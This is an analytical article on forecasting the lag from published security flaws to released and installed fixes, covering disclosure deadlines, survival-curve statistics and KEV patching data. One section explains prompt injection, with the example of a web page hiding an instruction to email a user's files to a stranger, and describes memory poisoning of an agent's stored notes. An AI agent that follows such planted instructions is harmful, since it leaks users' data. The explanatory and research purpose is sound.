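# Forecasting the lag between published AI security flaws and deployed fixes

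## What the lag is and how it is measured

A security flaw is a mistake in software that lets an attacker do something the owner never allowed, such as reading private files or taking over a computer. Users remain exposed to a published flaw until the vendor develops and releases a fix and that fix reaches their machines. This lag between publication and protection ranges from days to decades, and computer scientists have measured parts of it since at least 2000. It now matters for AI systems too, because companies are connecting them to email, files and program code.

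### One flaw from discovery to installation

PHP is a programming language that runs much of the web, including WordPress and Wikipedia. On 21 October 2026 its maintainers released emergency fixes for two flaws, together nicknamed PHP2Shell, that let an attacker without a login run commands on a web server. David (2026), in *Check Your PHP Version*, traces the history of one of them, CVE-2026-109618. (A CVE number is a flaw's public identifier.)

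In 2024, the security firm Quarkslab audited PHP. While fixing one of the audit's findings, a developer noticed a separate flaw. If PHP ran out of memory at the wrong moment, it left half-built data behind and later treated that data as valid. Nobody found a concrete way to attack this, and other bugs took priority. The security team drafted several fixes, but each had a drawback. One broke compatibility with older programs, another gave attackers a new way to crash the service, and a third needed changes to outside extensions that the team saw no way to coordinate. The work stalled and restarted for months. On 11 August 2026, a researcher at the security firm Calif reported a working attack with the same root cause, and the fix came out about ten weeks later.

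Arghire's *PHP2Shell Exploitation Started Days Before Patches* (2026) dates the first attempts to exploit PHP2Shell to 17 October, four days before the patch was released. OffSeq's *PHP2Shell in the wild* (2026) dates the first attempt against the firm's own decoy servers to the evening of 20 October, about sixteen hours before the patch. Both dates can be right, since a decoy records only the attacks that reach it.

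The release protected nobody until server owners installed it. Censys' *PHP2Shell Exposure Tracker* tracks installation by scanning the internet for servers that report their PHP version. It counts a server as patched on the day a scan first finds it running a fixed version, though the upgrade could have happened at any time since the previous scan. Owners still running PHP 8.1 or older have no official fix to install.

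### What "time to patch" can mean

How long, then, did PHP take to patch this flaw? There are at least five defensible answers.

| Clock starts | Clock stops | Result for PHP2Shell |
|---|---|---|
| First signs of the flaw, 2024 | Fix released, 21 October 2026 | About two years |
| Report of a working attack, 11 August 2026 | Fix released | 71 days |
| First attack attempt seen, 17 October 2026 | Fix released | 4 days |
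| Official announcement, 21 October 2026 | Fix released | 0 days |
| Fix released | A given server runs it | Different for every server |

*Fix time* is the number of days from the report of a flaw to its vendor until the vendor releases a fix. For PHP2Shell that is 71 days, though one could fairly count from 2024 instead, because the developer who first saw the problem was working for the PHP Foundation, which itself called the delay "a structural failure". *Installation time* is the time from the release of a fix until a given system runs it.

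Researchers have never settled on one set of intervals for measuring the lag. *Windows of Vulnerability* (Arbaugh, Fithen and McHugh, 2000) describes the life of a flaw as a series of states: birth, discovery, disclosure, correction, publicity, scripting and death. Scripting means packaging the attack so that people with little skill can use it. Death comes when so few vulnerable systems remain that the flaw no longer matters. The first three states must come in that order, but correction, publicity and scripting can follow in any order.

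One of their cases was phf, a small address-book program that came with two common web servers. Jennifer Myers published the flaw on 5 February 1996, and advisories explaining how to correct it followed within weeks. A script for the attack appeared in June. Reported break-ins did not rise much until August, and they continued until November 1998. Nearly all of that exposure was therefore installation time, when a fix was available but sites had not yet applied it. The numbers include only break-ins that victims chose to report, so they are too low, and a fall in reports may partly mean that people had lost interest.

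Frei, Schatzmann and colleagues (2009), in *Modelling the Security Ecosystem*, turned the states into six dates that a researcher can subtract from one another: creation, discovery, availability of an exploit (code or instructions that carry out the attack), public disclosure, availability of a patch, and installation. The dates mark off three periods of risk. Before disclosure, only an unknown group knows of the flaw. Between disclosure and the patch, anyone can know of it, and users are waiting for the vendor. After the patch, the delay depends mostly on the users. Frei and colleagues also pointed out that installation has no single date, because each user installs the patch on a different day, so a researcher can only describe it as a distribution over some population, such as home users or companies.

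Their waiting period for a patch starts at public disclosure. Kymberlee Price and Kouns (2015), in *Stranger Danger! What is the Risk from 3rd Party Libraries?*, objected to starting there because months can pass between the discovery of a flaw and a fix. Their Vulnerability Timeline and Exposure Metrics framework (VTEM) instead measures "time to patch" from the day the vendor hears of the flaw, which matches fix time as defined above. "Total time to patch" runs from discovery, and an organisation's "time of exposure" runs from the fix to its installation. The release date matters because a vendor can finish a patch without releasing it. In one case recorded in an attendee's notes on their talk, *BHUSA15* (2015), a vendor held back a finished patch for the next version of the product, and its customers stayed exposed for 451 days.

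Disclosure can also lag behind the fix. Sridharkumar, Al Hajj Ibrahim and colleagues (2026), in *Detecting Protracted Vulnerabilities in Open Source Projects*, collected 3,228 flaws that had left some trace, such as a bug discussion or a code change, at least a year before the US National Vulnerability Database published them. In a sample of 94, the median time to patch was 9 days and the median time to public disclosure was 619 days. Maintainers usually patched these flaws quickly, but users had little reason to hurry to update because nobody had told them the update fixed a security flaw. The sample was deliberately drawn from extreme cases, so its medians don't describe ordinary flaws.

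Installation time can be almost zero when the vendor runs the software itself. For this reason, *Events in a Vulnerability Lifecycle*, from CERT/CC, the coordination centre at Carnegie Mellon University, distinguishes between a fix that is ready and one that is deployed. Each user of *self-hosted* software must hear about the fix and install it, whereas the vendor of *hosted* software, such as a web-based chatbot, can change the product for everyone at once, and the public may never learn there was a problem.

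### Flaws, attack classes and failure modes

CVE-2026-109618 is one flaw in one product, and a specific fix removes it. An *attack class* is a general way of attacking many products. SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a web form, is an attack class, and many websites can each have their own SQL injection flaw. *Windows of Vulnerability* describes two flaws of another class, the buffer overflow, in the University of Washington's mail server. The first, made public in March 1997, let an attacker send an overlong username and overrun the memory set aside for it. The second came to light in July 1998 in another part of the login process, and the fix for the first had not removed it.

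A *mitigation* is any change that removes an attack or makes it succeed less often, and a fix is a mitigation that removes one flaw. An attack class can still work after thousands of fixes, so it needs its own measure. *Class lag* is the number of years from the first public description of an attack class until a protection is on by default in most deployed systems. Both dates require judgement, because it can be unclear which early paper or mailing-list post counts as the first description, and the point at which most deployed systems have the protection is usually an estimate. Fix time has clearer start and end dates, but a vendor can fix individual flaws quickly while the attack class behind them still works.

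The distinction between a flaw and an attack class matters a great deal for AI. A *language model* is a program, trained on large amounts of text, that produces text in response to text. An *agent* is a language model that can act through tools, for instance by running code, browsing the web or sending messages. In *prompt injection*, someone places text in material that an AI system reads, and the system follows it as an instruction. A web page might contain a hidden instruction to email the user's files to a stranger, and an agent may comply because the page and the user's request both reach the model as text. A vendor can fix one flaw by blocking the particular route by which the files left, but the attack class remains.

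Companies and researchers also publish weaknesses of AI systems more abstractly, as *failure modes*, the ways in which a kind of system can go wrong. The term comes from engineering, and Microsoft's *Taxonomy of Failure Mode in Agentic AI Systems* describes itself as a "failure mode and effects analysis", a study that lists a system's possible failures and their consequences. Microsoft's *New whitepaper outlines the taxonomy of failure modes in AI agents* (2025) explains how the list was made. The company's AI red team, whose job is to attack Microsoft's own products, catalogued what it had found in its own tests, had other groups at Microsoft vet the result, and interviewed outside developers of agents.

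The taxonomy classifies each failure as either security or safety, and as either novel or existing. Security failures compromise a system's confidentiality, integrity or availability, while safety failures harm users or society, for example when an agent serves some users worse than others without being instructed to. Novel failures are unique to agents, and existing failures are ones that other AI systems already had but that agents make more likely or more serious. Its worked example is memory poisoning, in which an attacker gets a malicious instruction into the notes an agent keeps between tasks, and the agent later recalls the instruction and carries it out.

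Publishing a failure mode starts the clock on a class lag at most, not on a fix, because no vendor has received a report and there is no version to update. Even for a class lag, the publication date may be the wrong starting point. Microsoft classed prompt injection through outside content as an existing failure in April 2025, so a lag counted from that month would be too short. Some entries may also never matter much in practice. Microsoft's *Updating the taxonomy of failure modes in agentic AI systems* (2026) reports that a year of attacks on deployed agents confirmed some of the original predictions and falsified others. Prompt injection through outside content was still the most reliable way to attack them. The update added seven failure modes, including abuse of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools and data.

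### Counting the flaws that are still open

Suppose a researcher tracks five flaws from the day each is reported. Vendors fix three of them after 20, 50 and 108 days. The other two are still unfixed when data collection ends, 60 and 90 days after they were reported. What is the typical fix time?

Two of the five flaws were still unfixed when observation ended, so all anyone knows is that their fix times exceed 60 and 90 days. Statisticians call such cases *censored*. The median of the three fixed flaws is 50 days, but this is too low because it leaves out the two slow cases. Counting those two as fixed on the last day of observation gives a median of 60 days, which is also too low because their actual fix times are longer.

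The standard remedy is a *survival curve*, which shows the share of flaws still open at each point in time after the starting date. The Kaplan–Meier method estimates it from incomplete data. On each day when a fix arrives, the method multiplies the running share by 1 − d/n, where d is the number of flaws fixed that day and n is the number still open and under observation just before. A censored flaw counts in n until observation of it ends, and its removal does not itself move the curve.

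| Day | Event | Open and observed just before | Calculation | Share still open |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | Clock starts | 5 | | 1.0 |
| 20 | One fix | 5 | 1.0 × 4/5 | 0.8 |
| 50 | One fix | 4 | 0.8 × 3/4 | 0.6 |
| 60 | Data end for one open flaw | 3 | no change | 0.6 |
| 90 | Data end for another | 2 | no change | 0.6 |
| 108 | One fix | 1 | 0.6 × 0/1 | 0 |

The median is the first day on which the share still open is one half or less. Here that is day 108, more than double the naive figure. The median is also called the *half-life*.

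A half-life estimated from five flaws is fragile. After day 90, a single flaw represents the three that were open after day 50, and if its vendor had taken 200 days to fix it, the estimate would be 200 days. If tracking had ended on day 108 with that flaw still open, the curve would never have reached one half, and the estimate could only have been "more than 108 days". The method also assumes that flaws that can no longer be tracked would have been fixed at the same pace as the rest. That assumption fails if, for example, a vendor stops answering questions because it has abandoned the product.

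The same curve can describe installation lag if it tracks machines instead of flaws, and class lag if it tracks attack classes. Censoring is unavoidable for class lag because the newest classes are the most likely to still be open.

### Why means and medians disagree

Householder, Chrabaszcz and colleagues (2020), in *Historical Analysis of Exploit Availability Timelines*, studied 75,807 flaws and found public exploit code for 3,164 of them. For those, the median time to publication of the exploit was 2 days and the mean was 91 days. Most exploits appeared almost at once, but a few appeared years later and raised the mean. For example, if nine exploits take 2 days each and one takes 892, the median is 2 days and the mean is 91.

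Neither number describes the typical flaw, because about 96% of the flaws in the study had no public exploit. Survival analysis treats these flaws as censored cases. Only 4.1% of all the flaws had an exploit within a year, so a survival curve that included every flaw would still be near 0.96 at that point, far above the 0.5 that marks the median. The claim that exploits appear within two days is true of flaws that get exploits, but people can identify those flaws only afterwards.

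The gap between mean and median persists in newer data. Zero Day Clock, which tracks the time from disclosure to exploitation, gives a median of 5.3 days and a mean of 127 days for exploited flaws from 2023, even though it drops the highest and lowest 5% of values before averaging. For 2018 it gives a median of 771 days. Part of the fall may be because flaws from 2018 have had eight years for late attacks to appear and raise the median, while flaws from 2023 have had about three.

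### How poor the public dates are

All of these methods need dates, but the public record has too few of them. Bonhomme and Dulaunoy (2026), in *Exploited Before It Was Fixed?*, tried to calculate how long attackers had been using flaws before a fix existed. They used only open, machine-readable sources: CVE records, vendors' and governments' advisories, reports of attacks, and catalogues of known exploited vulnerabilities. The best-known catalogue is the KEV list, to which the US agency CISA adds a flaw only when it has evidence of real attacks.

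On 3 November 2026, their data covered 3,758 exploited vulnerabilities. Of these, 98% had a disclosure date, but only 590 (15.7%) had a dated patch, and nine in ten of those patch dates came from Red Hat and Microsoft. None had a date for the report to the vendor, so fix time, the most basic measure of a vendor's performance, could not be calculated for any of them.

A vulnerability with no recorded patch date may still have a patch. Of the 3,168 vulnerabilities without a patch date, 821 had an undated link tagged as a patch. Bonhomme and Dulaunoy treat intervals with no patch date as censored, leaving them open instead of dropping them.

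Many exploitation dates are available, but about two thirds record only the day a catalogue listed the vulnerability. CISA, for example, listed 287 vulnerabilities on 3 November 2021, the day its catalogue began, though attackers had been using many of them long before. Only 875 dates were first-hand observations, nearly all from decoy servers. The authors excluded such bulk listings and pairs of dates whose order was unclear. That left 59 vulnerabilities whose recorded patch came after their recorded exploitation, with a median gap of 7.6 days. They say this gap is mostly the time from a catalogue listing to the first recorded fix, which is often a distributor's package that may have come out months after the original fix.

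Small filing errors changed the results substantially. In a first run, 40% of the exploitation dates were actually the dates when someone published exploit code, which a data feed had recorded as attacks. Correcting this cut the median gap from 39.5 days to 10.6. In another case, a publisher had added a 2026 vulnerability to a 2024 advisory, which made the wait for a patch appear to be 744 days when it was really 21.

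Publishers could close much of the gap in the data by adding the dates of the report, the acknowledgement and the fix to the records they already issue, and a draft standard for doing so exists. For now, some of this information is behind a paywall. The threat-intelligence company Flashpoint offers vendors' patching histories as proprietary data under the name VTEM.

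## From a report to a released fix: how long vendors take

The fix for PHP2Shell took 71 days, which is within the security industry's usual deadline. Under *coordinated disclosure*, whoever finds a flaw tells the vendor privately and allows a set period, commonly 90 days, to fix it. After that, the finder may publish the details even if no fix exists.

### The deadlines

Project Zero is a Google team that looks for flaws in widely used software, including Google's own. According to Project Zero (2019), its researchers let vendors choose the publication date for over a decade, and many fixes took more than six months while some never came. The team then set a 90-day deadline. A vendor that commits to a fix within two weeks of the deadline can get a 14-day grace period.

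The Zero Day Initiative (ZDI), run by the security company Trend Micro, buys flaws from independent researchers and passes them to vendors, according to TechTarget. Its *Disclosure Policy* gives vendors 120 days, after which ZDI publishes a limited advisory that includes advice on how users can protect themselves. When ZDI set its first deadline, which was six months, vendors had left about 120 of its reports unfixed, some for as long as three years, according to CRN's *HP's Zero Day Initiative Gives Vendors Patching Deadline*.

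Waiting 90 or 120 days makes sense only if nobody else is likely to find the same flaw in the meantime. *SoK* (Lbath, Suri and colleagues, 2026) cites a 2017 estimate that outsiders rediscover about 5.7% of privately held flaws each year. AI tools have probably raised that rate since then. In 2026, three parties reported the same PHP flaw within six weeks.

Disclosure deadlines are now shrinking for this reason. Silvanovich (2026), in *Policy and Disclosure*, called the repair timeline that Project Zero's policy had encouraged "clearly insufficient". The team will shorten its deadline to 60 days in February 2027 and 30 days in January 2028, as Arghire (2026) reported in *Google Project Zero Sets Course for 30-Day Disclosure Deadline*. Anthropic, an AI company that also reports flaws its models find, is cutting its deadline from 90 days to 30 for high- and critical-severity flaws and to 45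 for the rest, according to its *Updating our coordinated vulnerability disclosure policy timelines* (2026).

### A decade of steady medians

The longest record of fix times comes from ZDI, which publishes the dates of each report and release. Lbath and colleagues, a team led by the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), sampled 1,417 of ZDI's 14,738 advisories, spread across the quarters since 2016. For flaws that had a fix, the median time from report to release was between 96 and 119 days in every year from 2016 to 2026. The most recent quarter had the highest quarterly median, 148 days, but it covered only six weeks and 28 fixes.

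Google's developers now fix flaws in the Chrome browser faster. Lbath and colleagues calculated from Chrome's public bug tracker that the median time to fix an outside report was 50 days from 2020 to 2023, 44 days in 2025 and 36 to 45 days in 2026. Reports that named an AI system as the finder took 16 to 26 days. Those reports may concern more serious flaws or include better evidence, so the difference doesn't show that flaws found by AI are easier to fix.

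### Do deadlines set the pace?

ZDI's median fix times are close to its 120-day deadline. Vendors may need about 100 days to fix a flaw, or they may take that long because the deadline allows it.

Project Zero's record supports the second explanation, at least for some vendors. By July 2025, the team had reported 1,927 flaws under its rules with a grace period. Vendors fixed 1,629 of them within 90 days and 238 of the remaining 298 (80%) during the 14-day grace period. Most of these later fixes therefore came just in time to avoid publication, although one would expect flaws that had already lasted 90 days to be the hard ones, with fixes trickling in over the following months.

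Microsoft's recent fixes show the same pattern. Project Zero's *Reporting Transparency 2025* lists twelve Microsoft flaws that the team reported between July and December 2025, and each took between 75 and 103 days to fix. Microsoft's monthly update schedule may be part of the reason. Schoen (2022), who analysed Project Zero's reports from 2019 to 2021, suspected that the schedule made deadlines harder to meet and led the company to rely on the grace period. In 2026, though, Microsoft took only 8 and 19 days to fix two flaws that Project Zero had reported.

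The organisations that set deadlines also say the deadlines work. ZDI shortened its deadline from 180 days to 120, and Gorenc (2022), in *New Disclosure Timelines for Bugs Resulting from Incomplete Patches*, credits this with helping to reduce fix times. Project Zero saw one vendor respond 40% faster over seven years. Neither organisation had a comparison group, and vendors may have been getting faster anyway.

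Deadlines alone don't determine how long vendors take to fix flaws. In Schoen's data, Linux developers took an average of 25 days and Microsoft 83, though both had 90 days. Some open-source projects are fast even without a common deadline. Sridharkumar and colleagues cite a study of 369 flaws in packages for npm, the main library of JavaScript code, in which the median fix time was 11 days. But they also cite a study of Python packages in which the median was about two months, and maintainers fixed 41% of the flaws only after the details were public.

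Writing a fix often takes less time than releasing it. Schoen split the fix times of open-source browsers into the days until developers published the corrected code and the days from then until users could get it in a release. Chrome took an average of 5 days for the first step and 25 for the second. WebKit, the engine of Apple's Safari browser, took 12 and 61. A deadline can shorten the second step even if developers don't write fixes any faster.

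Deadlines most likely speed up slow vendors but make little difference to projects that fix flaws in a few weeks anyway. ZDI's steady median may therefore reflect its 120-day deadline more than how fast vendors can work. Project Zero's move to 60 days will be a good test. If fix times fall for its reports but not for ZDI's reports to the same vendors, the deadline is probably the cause.

Schoen urges caution in using any of these figures as a baseline. Vendors may treat Project Zero's reports as urgent because the team is trusted and will publish the flaw if a vendor misses the deadline. A flaw reported by an unknown researcher who sets no deadline could go unfixed for much longer.

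### Twice as many flaws

Fix times have held steady while the number of published flaws has risen sharply. Lbath and colleagues counted 89,749 new CVE records from January to October 2026, against 39,638 in the same months of 2025. The monthly count rose from 4,302 in January 2026 to 16,949 in October. Two thirds of the increase came from six organisations that issue CVE records: GitHub, VulnCheck, Oracle, the Linux kernel, Chrome and Microsoft.

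It's hard to say how much of this is due to AI. Only 2.4 to 2.8% of the records in each quarter of 2026 list an AI system as the finder, but most list no tool at all, so the true share is probably higher. The timing also suggests AI may have contributed. Epoch AI, a research group, counted about 2,500 high- and critical-severity flaws from 21 major organisations in July 2026. That was roughly five times the highest monthly count before April, when Anthropic announced Claude Mythos Preview, a model that can find and exploit flaws on its own. Epoch AI notes that people may also be looking harder. Project Zero now finds several flaws a week in products where it once found a few a year, according to Silvanovich.

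Users are no safer when vendors fix twice as many flaws but take just as long to fix each one, because twice as many known flaws are waiting for a fix at any moment. In a steady state, the number of open reports equals the number arriving per day multiplied by the average number of days each stays open. A vendor that receives 10 reports a day and takes an average of 100 days to fix each one has 1,000 open reports. If it receives 23 a day and its fix time stays the same, it has 2,300.

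The surge may also be too recent to affect the median. At ZDI's usual pace, a flaw reported in October 2026 gets its fix in January or February 2027, and statistics on released fixes can't include it until then. The latest quarter's 148-day median could be an early sign of overload or just noise from a small sample.

### The reports that nobody has fixed

ZDI's median covers only flaws that vendors fixed, so it may be too low, as in the earlier example with five flaws.

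By 3 November 2026, vendors had fixed 57 of the 107 flaws on Project Zero's *Reporting Transparency* list for the year, in a median of 42 days. The median was 75 days for the 37 fixed reports from June to December 2025, so vendors seem to have become almost twice as fast.

But 50 of the reports from 2026 were still open, 44 of them within the deadline and 6 past it. Applying the Kaplan–Meier method to all 107 gives a half-life of 71 days. This removes almost all of the apparent improvement, which arose because the 2026 list included the quick fixes but not yet the slow ones. The 71-day figure is rough because many of the reports concern the same Apple image software, and Apple tends to fix several flaws at once. Five of the six overdue flaws were in Google's own Android and Pixel products.

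Project Zero's reports at least get attention. Lbath and colleagues compared how many reports from different programmes ended in a fix and found very large differences.

| Programme | How the reports arrive | Reports | Share fixed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Big Sleep, Google's AI agent for finding flaws | Curated | 87 | 94% |
| Project Zero, 2019–2021 | Curated | 376 | 93% |
| OSS-Fuzz, automated testing of open-source code | Built into the project's own workflow | 23,907 | 71% within 90 days |
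| FuzzingBrain, an AI system | Curated | 62 | 58% |
| syzbot, automated testing of the Linux kernel | In bulk | 8,387 | 26% within 90 days |
| Anthropic, after review by a security firm | In bulk | 1,871 | 25% |
| Patch the Planet, run by the security firm Trail of Bits | In bulk | 2,118 | 24% |
| XBOW, an AI agent, through the bug-bounty site HackerOne | In bulk | 1,060 | 12% |
| Anthropic, sent directly | In bulk | 3,216 | 5% |

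The low shares may still rise, because the figures for Anthropic and Patch the Planet date from November 2026 and maintainers may yet fix many of the reported flaws. Lbath and colleagues also warn that the programmes differ in their targets and in the validity, severity and age of their reports, so the way a report arrives can't explain all the differences in the shares.

Inaccurate reports don't explain the low fix rates in the table well. Companies on HackerOne judged 72% of XBOW's closed reports genuine, yet only 12% of its reports had led to a fix. Even among Anthropic's reports that a security firm had checked first, only a quarter had led to a fix. Inaccuracy was a better reason to ignore some AI-written reports in 2025, when the maintainers of curl, a widely used tool for transferring data, could confirm only about 5% of the reports they received.

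The more likely bottleneck is the time of the people who must read each report, write a fix and test it. OSS-Fuzz and syzbot offer the fairest comparison, since both are automated and predate AI-based discovery. Within 90 days, developers fixed 71% of the flaws found by OSS-Fuzz, which was part of their own workflow, and 26% of those found by syzbot, which sent Linux kernel developers reports in bulk from outside. The kernel may simply be harder to fix than the average open-source project, but recent experience also suggests that fixes come faster when vendors do the testing themselves. Three vendors that used AI to search their own code released fixes at many times their earlier rate.

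A median fix time is close to meaningless for bulk reports because it covers only the flaws that have been fixed. Maintainers have fixed 165 of the 3,216 flaws that Anthropic sent them directly, so the median would describe about one report in twenty, however quickly those fixes were made.

### Fixes that did not work

The recorded fix time ends when the vendor releases a fix, even if the fix fails. Lbath and colleagues cite a study by Li and Paxson in which about 7% of 4,080 security fixes did not fully remove the flaw. If a vendor releases a faulty fix on day 100 and a working one 60 days later, the recorded fix time may be 100 days even though users waited 160 days for a fix that worked.

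*A Bug's Life*, by Franken, Van Goethem and colleagues, found that the median time from report to working fix was 44 days in Chromium, the open-source code behind Chrome, and 52 days in Firefox. The study covered 75 flaws in Content Security Policy, a browser feature that lets a website restrict which scripts may run on its pages. The researchers rebuilt the attack for each flaw and tested it on more than 100,000 versions of Firefox and of Chromium. Few researchers check whether old fixes worked, because it means running the attack again on many versions of the software.

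Three of the flaws were still open after developers had marked them as fixed. Each mistake was mundane:

- A website can set its policy in two ways, and the developers' test covered only one of them. The attack still worked on sites that used the other.
- Chromium's developers withdrew a working fix after 26 hours because it caused problems with Google Docs, but nobody changed the label on the report.
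- Firefox's fix passed its tests on a development build but failed in the packaged version that users installed.

Both browser makers keep reports confidential until users have the fix, so the wrong label also made the reports public, and anyone could read how to carry out an attack that still worked. At least two of the three flaws remained open for a year or more after that, and Mozilla fixed the Firefox flaw only when Franken and colleagues reported it again. Attempts to fix other faults in the same feature introduced twelve of the flaws. Three failures in 75 are too few to estimate a general rate, and Content Security Policy is an unusually complex feature.

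In 2022, after what Gorenc described as a decline in patch quality, ZDI tried to discourage faulty fixes by giving vendors shorter deadlines for second attempts. A vendor whose fix fails now gets 30 days if the flaw is critical and attacks are under way or imminent, 60 days if the flaw is serious but the first fix gives some protection, and 90 days otherwise.

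## From a released fix to an installed one: the record of known exploited vulnerabilities

The best evidence on how long owners take to install a released fix is about flaws on CISA's KEV list, which attackers are known to use. Organisations have more reason to patch these flaws than any others, so they probably take longer to patch the rest.

Organisations have good reason to install fixes quickly. According to Verizon's *2026 Data Breach Investigations Report* (2026), exploiting a flaw is now the most common way for attackers to get into an organisation, accounting for 31% of breaches. Verizon's analysis of patching used more than a billion records from Qualys, whose software scans customers' computers for known flaws. The full analysis is in Qualys' *The Broken Physics of Remediation* (2026). Qualys and Tenable, which also supplied data, both sell tools for finding and patching flaws,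 so they gain if customers conclude that patching by hand is failing.

### The survival curve

Qualys counts *instances*, meaning one flaw on one machine, so the same flaw on 200 laptops is 200 instances. Day 0 is the day CISA adds the flaw to the KEV list, and instances patched before then count as closed on day 0. Each year runs from November to October, so "2025" ends in October 2025.

| Days since KEV listing | Still open, 2022 | 2023 | 2024 | 2025 |
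|---|---|---|---|---|
| 7 | 61.5% | 70.7% | 60.0% | 68.1% |
| 28 | 44.6% | 34.8% | 27.0% | 35.0% |
| 91 | 32.4% | 19.4% | 14.6% | 20.6% |
| 182 | 25.8% | 11.7% | 9.2% | 13.4% |
| 364 | 18.0% | 7.3% | 5.1% | 9.0% |

A straight line between days 7 and 28 gives a half-life of just under two weeks in 2024 and between two and three weeks in 2025. After that the curve flattens. Owners who have not patched within three months often take many more months, and some may never patch.

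But part of the tail's rise from 5% to 9% may come from shorter follow-up of the 2025 instances. Qualys counts 47.3 million of them as open at day 364 and 47.1 million as open when observation ended. Because these numbers are so close, Qualys seems to have counted nearly everything still open at the end as open at day 364, even where CISA had listed the flaw only months earlier. For 2024 the numbers are 15.1 million and 10.7 million, presumably because owners had an extra year to deal with the remaining instances. Qualys acknowledges the shorter follow-up but expects it to make the tail look slightly better than it is. The comparison at day 28 is safer, since the problem affects only flaws that CISA listed in the last four weeks of the year.

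### Nine days, 43 days and 26%

Three other figures from the same research seem to contradict the curve. Qualys reports a median of 9 days to close an instance. Verizon reports a median of 43 days for "full resolution" of a KEV flaw, and found that organisations fully remediated only 26% of KEV flaws in 2025.

The 9-day median leaves out every instance that is still open. It is also measured from when a scanner first detects the flaw on the machine, which can be well after CISA listed it. The median for closed instances is 13 days when measured from the listing. Including the open ones raises it to the two to three weeks shown by the survival curve.

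Verizon's two figures appear to use a larger unit, one flaw across a whole organisation. CyberScoop's *Attackers hit vulnerabilities hard last year, making exploits the top entry point* (2026) quotes a passage in which 43 days is the median time for a vulnerability "to be fully patched". On that reading, a company that has patched 199 of its 200 laptops has closed 99.5% of its instances but has not fully remediated the flaw. Zafran's *Patches take weeks. Exploits take hours* (2026) reports that organisations had not remediated 16% of flaws at all. With 26% fully remediated, that leaves 58% partly remediated.

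By the end of observation, owners had closed 91.1% of the 2025 instances. That is consistent with finishing only 26% of flaws, because a flaw is finished only when every affected machine is patched. If each machine had a 91.1% chance of getting the patch, independently of the others, an organisation with 14 affected machines would patch all of them with probability 0.911^14, or about 27%. In practice patching isn't independent, because one administrator often patches many machines at once, but a few neglected machines per organisation are enough to produce both figures.

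The 43-day median probably leaves out unfinished cases too. If organisations have finished fixing only about a quarter of the flaws, the median for all of them would normally still be unknown, so 43 days is most likely the median for that quarter alone.

Verizon also compares the 43 days with 32 days the year before, but the two figures may cover different sets of flaws. In a summary of Verizon's 2025 report, GreyNoise (2025), a company that monitors internet attacks, gives 32 days as the median for *edge devices*, such as firewalls, which sit between an organisation's network and the internet. The median for all KEV flaws was 38 days. If the 43 days covers all KEV flaws, the real increase was 5 days instead of 11. The fall in the share fully remediated, from 38% to 26%, is not affected, because GreyNoise gives the 38% for all KEV flaws.

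Someone estimating how many machines remain exposed a month after a listing should use the survival curve. A company worried about a break-in should care more about full remediation, since an attacker may need only one unpatched machine.

### Older half-lives

Installation looks much slower when researchers include flaws that nobody is known to be attacking. Empirical Security's *Remediation Half‑Life* cites an older study of more than 500 firms and over 3 billion findings, in which the half-life for all vulnerabilities was 159 days. Speeds varied enormously between firms.

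The older study covered every kind of flaw, including thousands that a sensible administrator would leave until the next routine upgrade, while the KEV list is short and urgent. The roughly eightfold difference in speed therefore doesn't show that organisations have become that much faster. An earlier edition of Verizon's report is closer to the KEV figures. According to Telecompetitor's summary, organisations took 55 days to remediate half of critical vulnerabilities once patches were available.

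Patches have long been slow to reach the last machines. Lbath and colleagues cite a study in which a patch for software on company desktops and laptops could take more than six months to reach 90% of those machines.

### Why 2025 was worse than 2024

Qualys blames volume, arguing that teams worked as fast as before but had more to do than they could handle. The median time to close a KEV instance stayed at 9 days, while the number of instances in Qualys's records rose by 78%, from 295.8 million in 2024 to 527.3 million in 2025. CyberScoop reports that the median organisation had 16 KEV flaws to patch, up from 11.

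The 9-day median can't support that argument, because it excludes the instances that teams failed to close. The mean for closed instances fell from 32.0 days to 23.6 while the share still open rose at every point on the curve, as one would expect if more of the slow cases were still open and so missing from the average.

Qualys also measures from the date a scanner detects the flaw, and those figures suggest a different explanation. The share of instances still open a week after detection rose only from 58.3% to 60.2%, while the share open a week after the KEV listing rose from 60.0% to 68.1%. Organisations were therefore almost as fast in the first week after detection as they had been the year before, but the share of instances they had patched before CISA listed the flaw fell from 16.6% to 12.1%. That fall could account for up to 4.5 points of the 8.1-point rise measured from the listing.

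CISA's faster listing of flaws may have contributed. According to the security company Rapid7 (2026), the median time from a flaw's publication to its KEV listing fell in 2025. Earlier listings help defenders, but they leave owners less time to patch beforehand, so a curve that starts on the listing day looks worse even if nobody patches more slowly.

The mix of products also changes from year to year, which matters because patching times differ widely between products. Organisations took an average of 263 days to patch one flaw in IOS XE, the software on many Cisco routers and switches, and 459 days for a flaw in ActiveMQ, which passes messages between business programs. Tenable's *Key findings from the Verizon DBIR 2026* (2026) found the highest share of unpatched machines for flaws in development tools, followed by software for running virtual machines and tools for remote administration.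 The average share was above 50% in nearly every product category.

That sounds far worse than Qualys' 91% closure rate. One likely reason is that Qualys counts every machine equally, so a flaw on millions of laptops dominates the total, while Tenable's averages give more weight to flaws in less common products. Obscure server software can go unpatched for a year without noticeably changing Qualys' curve.

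In each of the four years, between 58% and 63% of instances were still open seven days after detection. In the passage Zafran quotes, Verizon suggests that this may be a "speed of light" for traditional patching. Testing, approval and scheduled maintenance take time in any large organisation, but a stable average is weak evidence of a limit, and some owners patched 63.7 million instances in 2025 before CISA had listed the flaws.

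### Federal deadlines

CISA started the KEV list in November 2021 under Binding Operational Directive 22-01, which ordered US federal civilian agencies to fix each listed flaw by a date given in the list. The directive's standard period was two weeks, or six months for flaws with CVE numbers from before 2021. In June 2026, CISA's Directive 26-04 set tiers of 3, 14 and 60 days. Companies, state governments and foreign organisations can follow the same list, but neither directive binds them.

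Patching got faster between 2022 and 2024, but the improvement can't be attributed to the first directive. The share of instances still open at day 28 fell from 44.6% to 27.0%, which is consistent with a public list of urgent flaws helping organisations to prioritise. However, 2022 was the list's first year, when many organisations were still learning to use it and CISA was adding large numbers of old flaws. The set of organisations and products that Qualys scanned also changed, and its global sample mixes organisations that must meet the deadlines with others that need not. A fair test would compare agencies with similar organisations outside the government, on the same flaws.

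The new tiers require agencies to patch faster than other organizations usually do. If agencies patched at the average pace of 2025, more than two thirds of instances would still be open when a three-day deadline, counted from the listing, expired. Between 35% and 68% would be open after 14 days, and between 21% and 35% after 60. Qualys' data end in October 2025, eight months before Directive 26-04, so they don't reflect any effect of the directive.

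### How fast attackers move

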